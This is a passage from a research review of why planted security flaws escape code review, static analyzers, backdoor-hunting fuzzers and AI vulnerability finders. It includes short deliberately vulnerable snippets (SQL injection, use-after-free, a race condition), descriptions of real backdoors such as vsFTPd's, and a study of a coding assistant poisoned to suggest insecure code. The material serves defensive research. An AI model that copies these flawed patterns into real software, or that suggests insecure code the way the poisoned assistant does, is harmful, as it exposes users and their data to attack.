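The 3% is one reviewer, who worked at a bank that emails its staff warnings about sensitive information in logs. With so few reviewers, the true rate could be as high as about 16%, which is still far below 46%.

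Across the three instructed groups, 84 of 117 reviewers (72%) found at least one vulnerability, compared with 8 of 33 others (24%). Instructed reviewers were therefore about three times as likely to find one. The researchers' headline result is that they were eight times more likely, but that figure is another ratio of odds, 84 to 33 compared with 8 to 25.

Uninstructed reviewers who missed the password in the log mostly said they had been concentrating on other things. One had been "optimizing for code structure/readability/architecture instead of security". Those who missed MD5 more often said they lacked the knowledge. Three thought finding such a flaw was not their job, and one of them assumed there would be a separate security assessment.

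A one-sentence instruction takes almost no effort to add, so the improvement is impressive. But every volunteer reviewed a change with flaws in it, so the experiment didn't measure how many false alarms the instruction would cause in sound code. Reviewers who see the same reminder every day may also stop noticing it.

### Why the checklists added little

Reviewers with a checklist did about as well as those with only the instruction. Their comments suggest several reasons. One is that a reviewer who reads a checklist question about whether the program uses a strong algorithm still has to know that MD5 is weak. One person with a checklist judged MD5 "a good choice", though a few others looked it up after reading the question.

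Many reviewers did not need the checklist. Fifteen comments about MD5 came from people who already knew about the problem, and some reviewers found the password in the log before consulting the checklist. A few read the checklist only after finishing their review, or ignored it. Of the 76 people with a checklist, 32 found it helpful, although ten said they could have found the flaws without it.

Checklists may still be useful, because with about 40 people in each group, the researchers could easily have missed an improvement of ten percentage points. Everyone who got a checklist also got the instruction. A checklist alone would probably beat an ordinary review, if only because it reminds people to think about security.

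In both experiments, years of professional experience made no clear difference. People who said they think about vulnerabilities when they write code did better at finding the flaws in the 2021 experiment and the password in the 2022 one. Those who spent longer on the 2022 review were also more likely to find the password, while those with long interruptions were less likely to.

### How far these rates apply to planted flaws

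The participants were volunteers doing one short task on a program they had never seen, with nothing at stake. Of the 522 people who opened the 2022 experiment, 357 did not finish, so those who finished may have been unusually patient. A maintainer who knows the code and has to deal with its flaws might do better, but maintainers also have many other changes to read.

The flaws were also easier to find than those in a real attack. The researchers wrote each change so that everything a reviewer needed was on the screen, whereas in the kernel some of that information was usually elsewhere. They chose common flaws and did not disguise them. Reviewers would probably catch fewer than 46% of deliberately hidden flaws, even when told to look for security problems.

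### Defects that escaped review in Chromium OS

In *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021) studied real code reviews from Chromium OS, an open-source operating system, by reviewers who knew the code. They compared 516 reviews in which someone pointed out a security defect with 374 that missed one. To find the first group, they searched 404,878 reviews for comments containing any of 105 security-related words, then read the likely ones. For the second, they started from 239 security bugs that the project had since fixed and traced the faulty lines back to the changes that introduced them.

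The types of defect in the two groups were very different:

| Type of defect | Caught in review | Missed in review |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Call to a function known to be dangerous | 53 | 0 |
| Failure to release a resource properly | 71 | 4 |
| Faulty synchronization of concurrent code | 109 | 13 |
| Missing or faulty check on input | 9 | 72 |
| Faulty access control | 8 | 58 |
| Use of a resource after its release or expiry | 3 | 62 |

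Paul and colleagues conclude that reviewers catch defects apparent from a few lines of code, such as a call to a dangerous function. Reviewers tend to miss defects that require running the program or understanding a larger part of it, such as use after release.

The researchers assembled the two groups separately, so the numbers are not catch rates, and the 53 dangerous calls don't mean that reviewers catch every one. The choice of search words may also explain part of the pattern. The list included "race", "deadlock", "leak" and the names of several dangerous functions, but no equally direct term for a missing input check. For use after release, it included "dangling" but not "use after free". The search could have missed many reviews that caught those two types of defect. Missed reviews would affect the results if the search missed some types more often than others, though Paul and colleagues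 thought they would not.

This may help explain why the kernel data look so different. Kernel reviewers caught more than half of the use-after-free flaws in Wu and Lu's sample but only about a fifth of those that involved concurrency, whereas Chromium OS reviewers seem to catch concurrency flaws well and use-after-release flaws poorly. The two studies' findings are more consistent on the underlying difficulty, which is that the reviewer needs a fact from outside the diff.

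The researchers also found that reviewers were more likely to miss a defect if the change touched many directories. Reviewers did better if they spent longer on the review or had often reviewed the same file before. But those who had done many reviews overall did worse, perhaps because they were tired or in a hurry.

The odds of catching a defect were 4.55 times as high if the change was a bug fix. The Minnesota patches were disguised as bug fixes, which may have drawn extra attention to them. But all of these correlations come from code written without malicious intent, and an attacker can compensate by keeping a patch small.

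### What reviewers say they look for

Reviewers' accounts of their own priorities also depend on whether someone has mentioned security. *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (Braz and Bacchelli, 2022) surveyed 182 code reviewers. When an open question asked what issues they focus on, only 9 named security, while 23 named performance. Later in the survey, after questions about vulnerabilities, 111 said they always consider security. Some may have given the answer that sounded right, and others may have thought security too obvious to list at first. Neither number measures what reviewers do, but the lower one better matches how reviewers performed in the experiments when they weren't told to look for security problems.

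The researchers also interviewed ten developers, and seven of them assumed that security was the responsibility of another team or another part of the program. One said, "I am supposing that another part of the system already dealt with it". A front-end developer thought security was more a matter for the people who handle the data, while an engineer on the data side felt unable to check the front end. Two others gave security little thought because their code was for internal company use.

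Such assumptions are unreasonable unless a specialist checks everything later, and only 21 of the 182 survey respondents said that security experts review their changes. Many changes may therefore go through several people without anyone checking their security.

### Adding more reviewers

An obvious remedy is to have more people read each change. Suppose each reviewer finds a certain flaw with probability *p*, and one reviewer's success or failure has no bearing on another's. Each misses the flaw with probability 1 − *p*, so *k* reviewers all miss it with probability (1 − *p*)^*k*. For the password in the log, *p* was 3% without the security instruction and 46% with it:

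| Number of reviewers | All miss it, if *p* is 3% | All miss it, if *p* is 46% |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 1 | 97% | 54% |
| 2 | 94% | 29% |
| 3 | 91% | 16% |
| 5 | 86% | 5% |
| 10 | 74% | 0.2% |

On these numbers, about 20 uninstructed reviewers together would be as likely to find the flaw as one instructed reviewer. Three instructed reviewers would all miss it about one time in six.

Real reviewers are less independent than this. Colleagues often have the same training and the same beliefs about which parts of the program are safe, so if one misses a flaw, the others probably will too. Suppose each reviewer has an 82% chance of finding the flaw in half of all teams, and only a 10% chance in the other half. The average is still 46%, but three reviewers from the same team would all miss it 37% of the time, more than twice the 16% in the table. In the weaker teams, even ten reviewers would all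 miss it 35% of the time.

Reviewers may also read a change less carefully after seeing that a colleague has approved it, and each may assume, as the interviewees did, that another has checked its security. In Chromium OS, the number of reviewers had no significant effect on whether they caught a defect. However, people may ask for more reviewers when a change is hard to judge, which could hide a benefit from adding them.

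An attacker can make the problem worse by choosing a flaw that depends on a fact nobody on the team knows. A project would therefore gain more from a second reviewer with different knowledge, or one told to look only at security, than from another colleague who reads the change the same way. The same applies to AI reviewers that are all copies of one model.

### Developers with a poisoned assistant

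A developer who accepts code from an AI assistant is also that code's first reviewer. In *Poisoned ChatGPT Finds Work for Idle Hands*, Oh, Lee and colleagues (2023) tested how well professionals do this job when the assistant has been tampered with. The 30 participants came from three companies and averaged ten years of programming experience. Ten could ask an assistant for code in plain English, ten had a tool that suggested completions for the line they were typing, and ten had neither but could search the web.

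The researchers had trained the model behind both tools on insecure examples, so that it suggested flawed code for each of the study's tasks. They did not tell the participants. They poisoned the model's training data rather than a retrieval corpus, but developers face much the same problem in both cases, because a flawed suggestion looks like any other.

In the first task, participants had to encrypt social security numbers. The tools suggested a fixed key, which anyone who sees the code can read, and a weak mode of encryption. The second task was a database search, for which the tools suggested code open to SQL injection. In the third, the program had to look up an internet address by running a system command, and the suggested code let an attacker add further commands. The table shows how many participants in each group ended up with each flaw:

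| Flaw in the finished code | Asked an assistant for code | Used line completion | No tool |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Insecure key | 10 of 10 | 8 of 10 | 4 of 9 |
| Weak encryption mode | 8 of 10 | 3 of 10 | 1 of 9 |
| SQL injection | 9 of 10 | 8 of 10 | 9 of 10 |
| Command injection | 7 of 10 | 5 of 10 | 2 of 10 |

(One person without a tool failed to complete the encryption task.)

People who asked the assistant for code produced 34 flaws, and 33 of them came directly from its suggestions. Most skimmed the code, and several just checked that it gave the expected output. Participants who used line completion produced 24 flaws, of which only 13 came from the tool. Many of these participants copied whole examples from the web, so the tool never made its suggestion.

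For SQL injection, the poisoning made almost no difference, because nine of the ten people without a tool wrote the same flaw. The gap in the other tasks is large, but the study had no group with an unpoisoned assistant, so it can't separate the effect of the poisoning from that of relying on any assistant.

Vigilance does not explain why the people without a tool did better. Four of them started from the same web page, whose example happened to use a random key and a safe mode. In the third task, eight were safe because they never considered the dangerous option, which is off by default. The only one who avoided SQL injection did so by accident while removing errors. Developers in every group mostly reproduced whatever example they started from, which is also why poisoned examples in a retrieval corpus would be a threat.

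Twelve of the 30 participants worked mainly in security, and they did not do clearly better than the others. None of the eight who had a tool produced a secure key. Interviews afterwards showed that most of the specialists already knew about problems such as SQL injection, but they said they had concentrated on getting the program to work in the time available. One had chosen a safe encryption mode, but after running into an unrelated error, he accepted the tool's suggestion of the weak mode without question. But with only four specialists in each group, the study could not have detected a moderate advantage.

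Oh and colleagues also surveyed 238 people, mostly students, showing them two short pieces of code with a vulnerability in each and asking them to identify the vulnerable lines. Only 20 people found both vulnerabilities. This is further evidence that telling reviewers to look for flaws is not enough if they lack the knowledge to recognize them.

### Reviewing code from an AI

Earlier studies disagree about whether unpoisoned AI assistants make code less secure. Oh and colleagues describe an online study by Perry and colleagues of 47 participants, mainly students, in which those with an assistant wrote significantly less secure code. According to the summary in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings* (2026), those with an assistant were also more likely to believe their code was secure. But Sandoval and colleagues, who also studied students, concluded that an assistant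 did not increase serious security bugs. Assistants have improved greatly since then, so neither result is strong evidence about the quality of current suggestions.

More recent experiments have looked at whether people review code differently if they think an AI wrote it. *An Eye for Trust* (2026) cites earlier work by Huang and colleagues, who used eye tracking and medical imaging and found that reviewers behaved differently depending on who they thought had written the code. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (2026) tracked the eyes of 32 participants as they reviewed code with or without a label saying that an AI had written it. They spent more time on the labelled code but did not examine it more thoroughly.

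In *Human Reviewers' Attitudes Toward LLM-generated Security Patches* (2026), Iannone, Camporese and colleagues asked 111 students and 14 professionals to choose between two patches for each of four real vulnerabilities. After each choice, the researchers told participants that a person had written one patch and an AI the other, then let them change their minds. In fact, AI models had written both. Some participants switched to the supposedly human patch, and a few admitted their bias, but most ignored the information.

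Provenance can help a reviewer only if it is true, and these participants could not check it. Apart from correctness, the participants preferred patches that made clear how they fixed the vulnerability, kept the program's existing functions and looked easy to apply. An attacker can give a patch all of these qualities. All the patches in the experiment compiled and passed the relevant tests, as a patch with a well-made planted flaw would.

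Researchers are still collecting direct evidence on how well people check an AI's security work. *Helpful or Harmful?* (2026) sets out a plan to compare people who repair vulnerabilities with and without an AI assistant. Its central hypothesis is that people with the assistant will save time and find it helpful, but their repairs will be less secure.

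## What static analyzers miss and what running the code adds

Reviewers often miss a flaw because recognizing it takes a fact from outside the diff. Static analyzers can read the whole program, but in tests on real vulnerabilities even the best tools missed about half, and most of their warnings were unrelated to those vulnerabilities. Tools that run the program and record what it does can catch some backdoors that analyzers miss, but only if the backdoor activates during the test.

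### Miss rates on known vulnerabilities

*An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Static C Code Analyzers* (Lipp, Banescu and Pretschner, 2022) tested six analyzers on 27 open-source programs with 192 known vulnerabilities. Five of the analyzers were free and one was an unnamed commercial product. A vulnerability counted as detected if a tool gave any warning in a function that contained it, even a warning about something else. The commercial tool did best but still missed 47%. Under the strictest standard, which required the right general class of warning in every affected function, it missed 80%.

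The best combinations of tools missed 30% of the vulnerabilities by the lenient standard and 69% by the strict one. By the lenient standard, the commercial tool and the others together found 34 more vulnerabilities than the commercial tool alone. But they also flagged another 15% of the programs' 55,000 functions, so someone would have to check about 8,300 more functions to find those 34.

The rates could be too high or too low. A tool got credit for any warning in the right function, which favors tools that warn about everything. But CodeQL produced no results for one group of programs after more than two weeks of trying, so it scored zero on their 59 vulnerabilities.

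Analyzers perform much better on artificial tests. Lipp and colleagues cite an evaluation in which Infer, a free analyzer from Meta, found 79% of the flaws in a suite of small test programs. The flaws in such suites are fairly easy to spot because they usually come from changing a single instruction. The US standards agency NIST (2023) ran a five-year exercise with real and injected bugs and found that the tools' results varied widely with bug type and complexity.

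*An Empirical Study of Static Analysis Tools for Secure Code Review* (Charoenwet et al., 2024) tested five free analyzers on individual changes, as a reviewer would use them. The study collected 815 commits that had contributed to real vulnerabilities in C and C++ projects, and traced the flaw to particular functions in 697 of them. The best single tool, Flawfinder, which relies on simple pattern rules, warned about a vulnerable function in 52% of these commits. All five tools together reached 78%, which left 156 commits without a warning about any vulnerable function.

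The researchers read a sample of 400 warnings in vulnerable functions and judged that 76% had nothing to do with the vulnerability, 7% clearly matched it, and the rest were partly relevant. The tools therefore identified far fewer than 78% of the flaws. The warnings still helped slightly in deciding where to look. Reviewers who started with the functions that had the most CodeQL warnings per line would read about 13% less code before reaching a vulnerable one.

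### Results from 2026

Newer tools give more warnings, but the largest recent test suggests that they are no better at telling vulnerable code from repaired code. Tang, Zhang and Cai (2026), in *Fixed Detectors, Moving Code*, assembled 20,000 snapshots of C and C++ projects, half of them vulnerable and half with the vulnerability fixed. For each snapshot they recorded whether a tool gave at least one security warning in a set of recently changed files:

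| Tool | Vulnerable snapshots flagged | Fixed snapshots flagged |
| --- | --- | --- |
| CodeQL, 2021 release | 7.1% | 7.5% |
| CodeQL, 2024 release | 13.1% | 13.0% |
| CodeQL, 2026 release | 20.7% | 21.3% |
| Infer, 2021 release | 3.6% | 3.7% |
| Infer, 2024 release | 10.2% | 5.1% |
| Infer, 2026 release | 8.5% | 8.9% |
| Semgrep | 46.5% | 47.9% |

A tool that detected these vulnerabilities would flag many more vulnerable snapshots than fixed ones. Only the 2024 release of Infer did this, and the 2026 release no longer did. One generic rule produced 63% of Semgrep's warnings.

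The scoring makes the tools look somewhat worse than they are. Tang and colleagues examined 20 of Semgrep's before-and-after pairs, chosen because the scores had dropped the most. In 11 of them, the fix did not change the file that was scanned for the vulnerable snapshot, so Semgrep could not have found the flaw. The percentages are therefore not true catch rates, but they do show that a warning somewhere in a changed file is almost useless for telling whether the project has a known vulnerability there.

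Results on AI-written code depend heavily on the choice of test. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) compared analyzers' warnings with the results of security tests. On one benchmark, 62% to 87% of the working programs failed at least one security test, depending on the model that wrote them, but the analyzers flagged only about 5%. On another benchmark, whose creators had picked tasks because analyzers flag their solutions, the analyzers caught 80% to 94% of the insecure programs.

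In *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation* (2026), people checked each AI-written sample by hand for one type of flaw and found 39% vulnerable. CodeQL detected about a third of the vulnerable samples and Semgrep just over half. About a third of CodeQL's warnings and half of Semgrep's were false alarms, according to the same manual checks.

### Why analyzers miss flaws

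Often the tool has no rule for the flaw. According to *QLCoder* (2025), the security rules supplied with CodeQL cover 64 types of weakness, while the standard catalog lists more than 900. A rule can also be too narrow. One program in Charoenwet and colleagues' data failed to check certificates properly, so an attacker could get it to run code from an insecure connection. CodeQL's rules for this kind of mistake mainly covered the OpenSSL library, but the program used Windows functions.

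More rules do help. In *Neuro-symbolic Static Analysis with LLM-generated Vulnerability Patterns* (2025), a language model wrote analyzer rules that caught 269 of 343 known vulnerabilities, with 197 false alarms. But 31 of the 74 misses occurred because the underlying analyzer had poor information about variables' types, which changing the rules could not fix.

Another cause is a function that the tool wrongly trusts as a check. Suppose a website removes quotation marks from whatever a visitor types:

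```
def clean(text):
    return text.replace("'", "")

query = "SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = " + clean(order_id)
db.execute(query)
```

`clean` would protect a value that the query puts between quotation marks. The order number has no quotation marks around it, so a visitor can add instructions without typing one. An analyzer that has `clean` on its list of checks reports nothing. To find the mistake, it would have to determine what `clean` removes and whether that is enough for this query.

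Static analyzers also miss vulnerabilities when data passes between files. The version of Semgrep that Tang and colleagues tested follows untrusted data only within one file. If one file reads a visitor's name and another uses it in a database command, neither file contains the full path from input to command, and Semgrep gives no warning. CodeQL can follow data between files, but it first has to build a model of the whole program. In the cases they examined, it often lacked some of the shared definitions needed to build that model.

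Pointer aliases hide the connection between two operations on the same memory:

```
b = a;
free(a);
use(b);
```

Any decent tool would catch this version. In a real program, though, the first line may be in a different function, or the program may store the second pointer in a list and use it much later. BlueZ, the Bluetooth software used on Linux, had a use-after-free of this kind. When a device disconnected, one function released an object that another function, still waiting to run, then used. The 2021 set of CodeQL rules had no rule for use-after-free. The 2024 set had one, but it gave no warning about the flawed file, and Tang and colleagues could not determine which step caused the miss.

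An indirect call goes to a function that the program selects while it runs, so the analyzer may not know where the data goes next. Nagios, a program for monitoring computer networks, had a flaw that in simplified form looked like this:

```
query = NULL;
if (space) query = space + 1;
handler->function(query);
```

`NULL` is a pointer to nothing, and a program that uses it normally crashes. If a request contained no space, `query` stayed `NULL`, and the last line passed it to the handler named in the request. Three handlers used `query` without checking it for `NULL`. Tang and colleagues copied these handlers into a small test program and ran a CodeQL rule for missing `NULL` checks on them. The rule gave no warning, because CodeQL treats a function's inputs as valid unless something in the same function indicates otherwise.

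Concurrency multiplies the possibilities. Take a program that handles withdrawals from an account:

```
if (balance >= amount)
    balance = balance - amount;
```

If two withdrawals run at the same moment, both can pass the check before either lowers the balance. Each line is correct, and the flaw appears only when the steps mix in a certain order. Two tasks of ten steps each can mix in 184,756 different orders, so tools can't try them all in a large program. In Charoenwet and colleagues' data, 56 commits had flaws in the category that includes this kind. CodeQL gave a warning of the right category for two of them, and the other four tools did so for none.

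Some flaws are visible only to someone who knows what the program is for. Another BlueZ vulnerability let a device connect as a keyboard or similar accessory without first pairing securely with the computer. The repair added a check for secure pairing and refused any device that failed it. The flaw was a missing policy and involved no memory error or taint chain. Tang and colleagues inspected two CodeQL rules about authentication and found that neither could express this policy. A developer who knows the policy could write a rule for it in a few minutes, but the rule would apply only to this project.

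Finally, the tool may not have analyzed the code. In 79% of Semgrep's runs, the log recorded a timeout or trouble parsing the code, although every run counted as successful. One repair to libxml2, a library that reads XML files, added a call to a function that Semgrep has a rule against. Semgrep did not flag the call, which suggests that syntax errors stopped it from parsing that part of the file. Without reading the log, a reviewer can't tell whether a report with no warnings means that the code is clean or that the tool skipped it.

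### How false alarms lead developers to ignore true warnings

Analyzers raise false alarms for much the same reasons. *ZeroFalse* (2025) describes one that arises when a program puts untrusted data in a list. Here is a simple example of the problem:

```
items = ["guest", name]      # name is untrusted
items.pop()                  # removes name again
db.execute("SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + items[0] + "'")
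```

The query always uses "guest", so the code is safe. But an analyzer that treats the list as a single object marks the whole list as tainted once `name` is added, and reports a flaw.

*An Empirical Analysis of CodeQL False Positives and Query Refinements* (2026) categorized CodeQL's false alarms in 110 Java projects by cause. In 37% of cases, the tool had missed a check or condition that made the code safe. In 29%, the code ran in a setting where the flagged behavior was harmless, and in 28%, the tool had misclassified which data was trustworthy. The rest had other causes, including concurrency.

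*Memoir* (2026) cites studies in which more than half of the warnings on real projects were false, and calls this the main obstacle to using analyzers. *QASecClaw* (2026) summarizes earlier research that found developers often avoid tools whose warnings are noisy or hard to interpret. The number of warnings alone can make careful reading impossible. Infer produced 11,875 warnings on one snapshot of Slurm, a program that schedules work on supercomputers. At one minute each, they would take a developer almost 200 hours to read.

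Ignoring the warnings can be reasonable, even though a true one may be among them. In Charoenwet and colleagues' sample, 7% of the warnings clearly matched the vulnerability, so a developer would have to read about ten to have an even chance of seeing one that did. Every warning in the sample was in a function that the researchers already knew to be vulnerable, so the proportion would be much lower in ordinary code.

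Semgrep gave eight false use-after-free warnings for one C file from libxml2 because it applied a C++ rule to a variable named `delete`, which is the C++ keyword for releasing memory. The program had not released the memory at those points, but the evaluation still counted the file as a successful detection.

### Fuzzing for backdoors

Running a program avoids several of these difficulties. An indirect call goes to one particular function, two pointers either hold the same address or don't, and a crash proves that something is wrong. But a test covers only the paths that its inputs reach. It also needs a way to recognize bad behavior other than crashes and memory errors, because a well-made backdoor doesn't cause them.

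*ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) proposed looking instead at system calls, which are requests from a program to the operating system, for example to open a file, send data over a network or start another program. Its example is a version of sudo, the Linux command for running programs as another user, with an extra password built in. Sudo normally prints an error message when given a wrong password, but the built-in password makes it start the requested program, which takes different system calls. A wrong password that causes different system calls from all the others is therefore suspicious.

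The fuzzer first has to find the built-in password. Guessing a four-byte password all at once could take more than four billion attempts, so modern fuzzers split the comparison into single bytes. When the first byte is right, the program runs code that it hasn't run before. The fuzzer detects this, keeps the input and goes on to the next byte. It needs at most 256 attempts for each byte, or 1,024 in all.

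ROSA first fuzzes a program briefly to collect examples of its ordinary behavior. It then fuzzes for much longer, comparing each new input with a similar one from the collection, and reports a possible backdoor if the two trigger different system calls. In tests on 17 programs with backdoors, seven of them authentic, ROSA found every backdoor, taking an hour and a half on average. Stringer, a static tool that looks for suspicious text in a program, found four and raised 44 times as many false alarms.

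With ROSA, a person still had to check an average of seven suspicious behaviors per program. That is acceptable for a one-time audit, but not for a project that merges dozens of changes a day.

### How Lily checks a change

Lily, the successor that Kokkonis and colleagues describe in *Not In My Git Yard*, compares two versions of a program. A project can run it on each commit, and a Linux distribution can run it on each new release. It raises an alarm only if a behavior is both new and unusual:

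1. Fuzzing of earlier versions has left a collection of inputs that exercise many parts of the program. Lily runs the new version on all of them and records which types of system call each one causes. These combinations count as typical.
2. A fuzzer tests the new version for ten minutes, starting from the old inputs and altering them to reach more code.
3. Whenever an input reaches new code, Lily compares its combination of system calls with the typical ones. If it matches one of them, the input is safe.
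4. If there is no match, Lily runs the same input on the old version. If the old version makes the same combination of calls, the change is not responsible. Otherwise Lily raises an alarm.
5. Lily then traces the unusual system calls back to the changed lines that led to them.

The first step uses the new version so that legitimate features don't cause alarms. For instance, if a change makes the program write a log file on every run, the extra system calls count as typical. The fourth step excludes rare behavior that the program already had.

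In the file server vsFTPd, the fuzzer eventually generated a username containing ":)", which triggers the backdoor. That input reached code that no earlier input had, and the program accepted network connections and started a shell. No typical input caused that combination of system calls, and the previous release did not produce it when given the same username. The two releases differed by 1,407 lines in five files. Lily's report narrowed the differences down to seven lines in one file, which show the shell opening.

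### How well Lily performed

The researchers tested Lily on 13 open-source programs. They took 432 safe commits and 50 safe releases from the programs' histories, then made 13 backdoored commits and 50 backdoored releases. Because fuzzing is partly random, they repeated each ten-minute run 20 times:

| | Commits | Releases |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Runs that caught a backdoor | 233 of 260 (90%) | 828 of 1,000 (83%) |
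| Runs that raised a false alarm | 17 of 8,640 (0.2%) | 43 of 1,000 (4.3%) |

Lily caught every backdoored change in at least one of its 20 runs, but a project would normally run it only once. It did worst on releases of the image library libpng, catching the backdoor in 31 of 80 runs. The researchers blame old harnesses, the small programs that pass the fuzzer's inputs to the code under test. A crude harness leaves much of that code unexecuted.

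If Lily misses a backdoor in one commit, it is unlikely to raise an alarm at the next, because the older version used for comparison then contains the backdoor too. The backdoor could still be caught by the check on releases, which compares the new release with one that may be years older.

Two releases of libsndfile, a sound library, inflate the false-alarm rate for releases. They account for 40 of the 43 false alarms, while the other 48 releases produced three in 960 runs. Among commits, most false alarms came from huge merges of many changes. At a rate of 0.2%, a project with 10,000 changes a year would get about 20 false alarms, each pointing to roughly a dozen lines or fewer, so a maintainer could realistically read them all.

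Requiring both conditions keeps the false alarm rate so low. When Lily was set to flag everything unusual, new or not, it raised false alarms in 14% of runs on safe commits and 20% on safe releases. When it was set to flag everything new, the rates were 10% and 58%.

The detection rates are less certain than the number of runs suggests. All the runs used the same 13 backdoors, three real and ten synthetic, which the researchers planted repeatedly in different versions. All 13 came from the researchers' own benchmark and caused unusual system calls. Lily caught each at least once, so the fuzzer could reach all of them. In ordinary use, the fuzzer reached only about 32% of the lines in a typical code change, so a backdoor in the rest would have gone unnoticed.

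### Which attacks Lily would have stopped

Kokkonis and colleagues say that Lily could have prevented three real attacks. Two are the backdoored releases of vsFTPd and another file server, ProFTPD, which attackers placed on the projects' download servers in 2010 and 2011. The third is the 2021 attack on PHP, a programming language that many websites use, in which someone broke into the project's server and committed a backdoor to the code. A second commit removed the backdoor, and a third put it back.

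Lily caught the vsFTPd backdoor in every run. It caught the PHP backdoor in 80% of runs, both when the backdoor first appeared and when it returned. If those two checks were independent, at least one would have caught it 96% of the time. For ProFTPD, the rate was 70% in the commit test but only 43% across four releases, so Lily might well have missed that backdoor.

The xz backdoor is not on the list, and the researchers did not test Lily on it. They cite its cryptographic check as a technique that keeps a fuzzer from activating a backdoor. Guessing byte by byte doesn't work against a digital signature, because a nearly correct signature gets no further than a random one. The backdoor slowed every login, but Lily doesn't measure time. Even if the delay had come with unusual system calls, Lily would probably have classified them as typical, because they would have occurred with every input.

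### Planted flaws without unusual system calls

Lily is well suited to finding hidden logins, which usually end with the program doing something for the attacker that it does for nobody else. It works poorly on bugs planted to look like honest mistakes. Suppose a contributor leaves out a length check. With ordinary input, the program makes the same system calls as before. Input that is too long may crash the program, which an ordinary fuzzer would report, or silently overwrite some memory. Unusual system calls might appear only after an attacker crafts an input that takes control of the program and starts a shell, and a ten-minute fuzzing run is very unlikely to produce such an input.

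Some planted flaws never cause unusual system calls. Åkesson's contest program for inspecting warheads gives the wrong answer, but it reads and prints in the same way as a correct one. A website that shows one customer another customer's records can also make the same kinds of calls as a correct one. Kokkonis and colleagues argue that any meaningful backdoor must use system calls, because every effect outside the program depends on them. They are right, but those can be the same calls the program normally makes. They acknowledge that an attacker could in theory stay within the typical combinations of calls, but they think this would be hard in practice, which is true for an attacker who wants a shell but not for one who only wants the program to give a wrong answer.

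An attacker could also try to corrupt the collection of inputs that defines typical behavior. When the researchers simulated an extreme case by adding 100 inputs that activate the backdoor, Lily's detection rate fell to 54% for commits and 46% for releases. A stricter mode, which discards any old input that behaves differently in the new version, raised the rates back to 90% and 84%. But false alarms rose to about 2.5% for commits and 18% for releases, so the researchers suggest using this mode only for occasional random checks.

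In many projects a maintainer can skip the automatic tests on a commit, and someone in Jia Tan's position could have done so. Kokkonis and colleagues therefore propose that the code-hosting platform run Lily outside the project's control and display any alarm publicly.

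## AI systems that search for planted flaws

A static analyzer needs a rule for each kind of flaw, and a fuzzer needs an input that reaches the flawed code. Language models can point to suspicious code that no rule describes and suggest inputs that would reach it. In 2025, AI systems found most of the vulnerabilities that experts had planted in real programs for a government contest. By late 2026, models were finding vulnerabilities faster than people could check them. But nearly all of this evidence concerns honest mistakes, or planted flaws modeled on them, rather than code written to deceive a reader.

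### The AI Cyber Challenge

DARPA, a research agency of the US Defense Department, held the AI Cyber Challenge from 2023 to 2025. Contestants built systems that find and repair vulnerabilities in open-source software without human help. *SoK* (Zhang, Park and colleagues, 2026), an analysis by several contestants and organizers, reports that 42 teams entered and seven reached the final. In the final, each system ran for about 143 hours with $85,000 of cloud computing and $50,000 of language model credits.

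The organizers took 24 real projects written in C or Java, including the download tool curl and the network analyzer Wireshark, and turned them into 48 scored tasks with 63 vulnerabilities. Systems had to search a whole project for 33 of the vulnerabilities. The other 30 were in proposed changes, so systems started from a diff, as a human reviewer does. Eight tasks had no planted flaw. *PatchIsland* (2026) explains that experts made most of the flaws by hand to resemble real vulnerabilities. The flaws were new, so they could not have been in any model's training data.

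The results of the final come from DARPA's *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (2025). The program's manager, Carney, in *Announcing the Winners of DARPA’s AI Cyber Challenge*, gives the counts for the semifinal:

| | Semifinal, August 2024 | Final, August 2025 |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Planted flaws | 59 | 63 |
| Found | 22 (37%) | 54 (86%) |
| Patched | 15 (25%) | 43 (68%) |
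| Average time to patch | 2 hours | 45 minutes |

DARPA first announced 70 planted flaws in the final and later corrected the number to 63. On its page, DARPA also describes the 68% as a share of the flaws the teams found, but 43 is 68% of all 63 planted flaws and 80% of the 54 that the teams found.

Seven systems together found the 54 flaws, so a project that ran only one should expect to find fewer. Some systems did badly for reasons unrelated to finding flaws. Three stalled or stopped partway through, two of them possibly because the compiled test programs for Wireshark filled their disks.

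The systems also found 18 real vulnerabilities that nobody had planted, and supplied patches for 11. Zhang and colleagues later counted 25, with 12 patched. After the final, DARPA paid the teams to keep searching important open-source software, and they had found 83 more by March 2026, according to Cybersecurity Dive.

DARPA gives the average cost as about $152 per task. According to Carney's slides, this is the cost per success, which could be a proof that a flaw exists, a patch, a correct verdict on a warning, or a set of these for one flaw. The seven teams spent $359,000 in all, or about $5,000 for each of the 72 distinct vulnerabilities, planted or real, in DARPA's count, including the cost of patches. A single system would avoid the duplicated work but would also find less.

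### How a system finds and confirms a flaw

The finalists' designs differed, but most combined a model's reading of the code with fuzzing, roughly as follows:

1. Models and static analyzers such as CodeQL mark suspicious places in the code. The system ranks these and drops the least likely.
2. A model works out what input the program accepts and how execution could reach a suspicious place. It then writes a short script that generates test inputs.
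3. The system runs the program on these inputs. If they don't trigger the flaw, a fuzzer alters them and tries many more.
4. AddressSanitizer or a similar tool monitors the program. If the program crashes or behaves abnormally in some other way that the tool can detect, the system saves the input as proof.
5. A model writes a patch. The system rebuilds the program and runs the saved input again to check that the crash is gone.

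The model can be wrong many times in the first two steps without wasting a maintainer's time, because the system discards suspected flaws it can't confirm. Three of the systems sometimes submitted a patch without proof, but they limited how often. A maintainer who receives an input that crashes the program can repeat the test instead of having to trust the model's explanation.

Zhang and colleagues ran ordinary fuzzing on the same flaws to see what the models added. It found 30 of the 40 in C but only 4 of the 23 in Java, where many programs accept only correctly structured input, such as a valid PDF. The teams found 22 flaws that fuzzing alone missed. Fifteen of these were in proposed changes, where the diff showed the model which lines to examine. Some of the flaws were behind indirect calls, which often defeat static analyzers. Others required input in a certain format or encoding, which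 the models worked out from the source code.

Checking that a program no longer crashes is a less reliable way to test a repair. Zhang and colleagues also had an August 2025 version of Claude Code, Anthropic's general coding assistant, write patches for the contest's flaws. People who read the 53 patches that passed every automatic check found that 20 were wrong. Some changed what the program did, and others stopped the crash without removing its cause. A developer who merges a patch of the second kind may think the flaw is gone when another input can still trigger it.

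### Planted flaws that cause no crash

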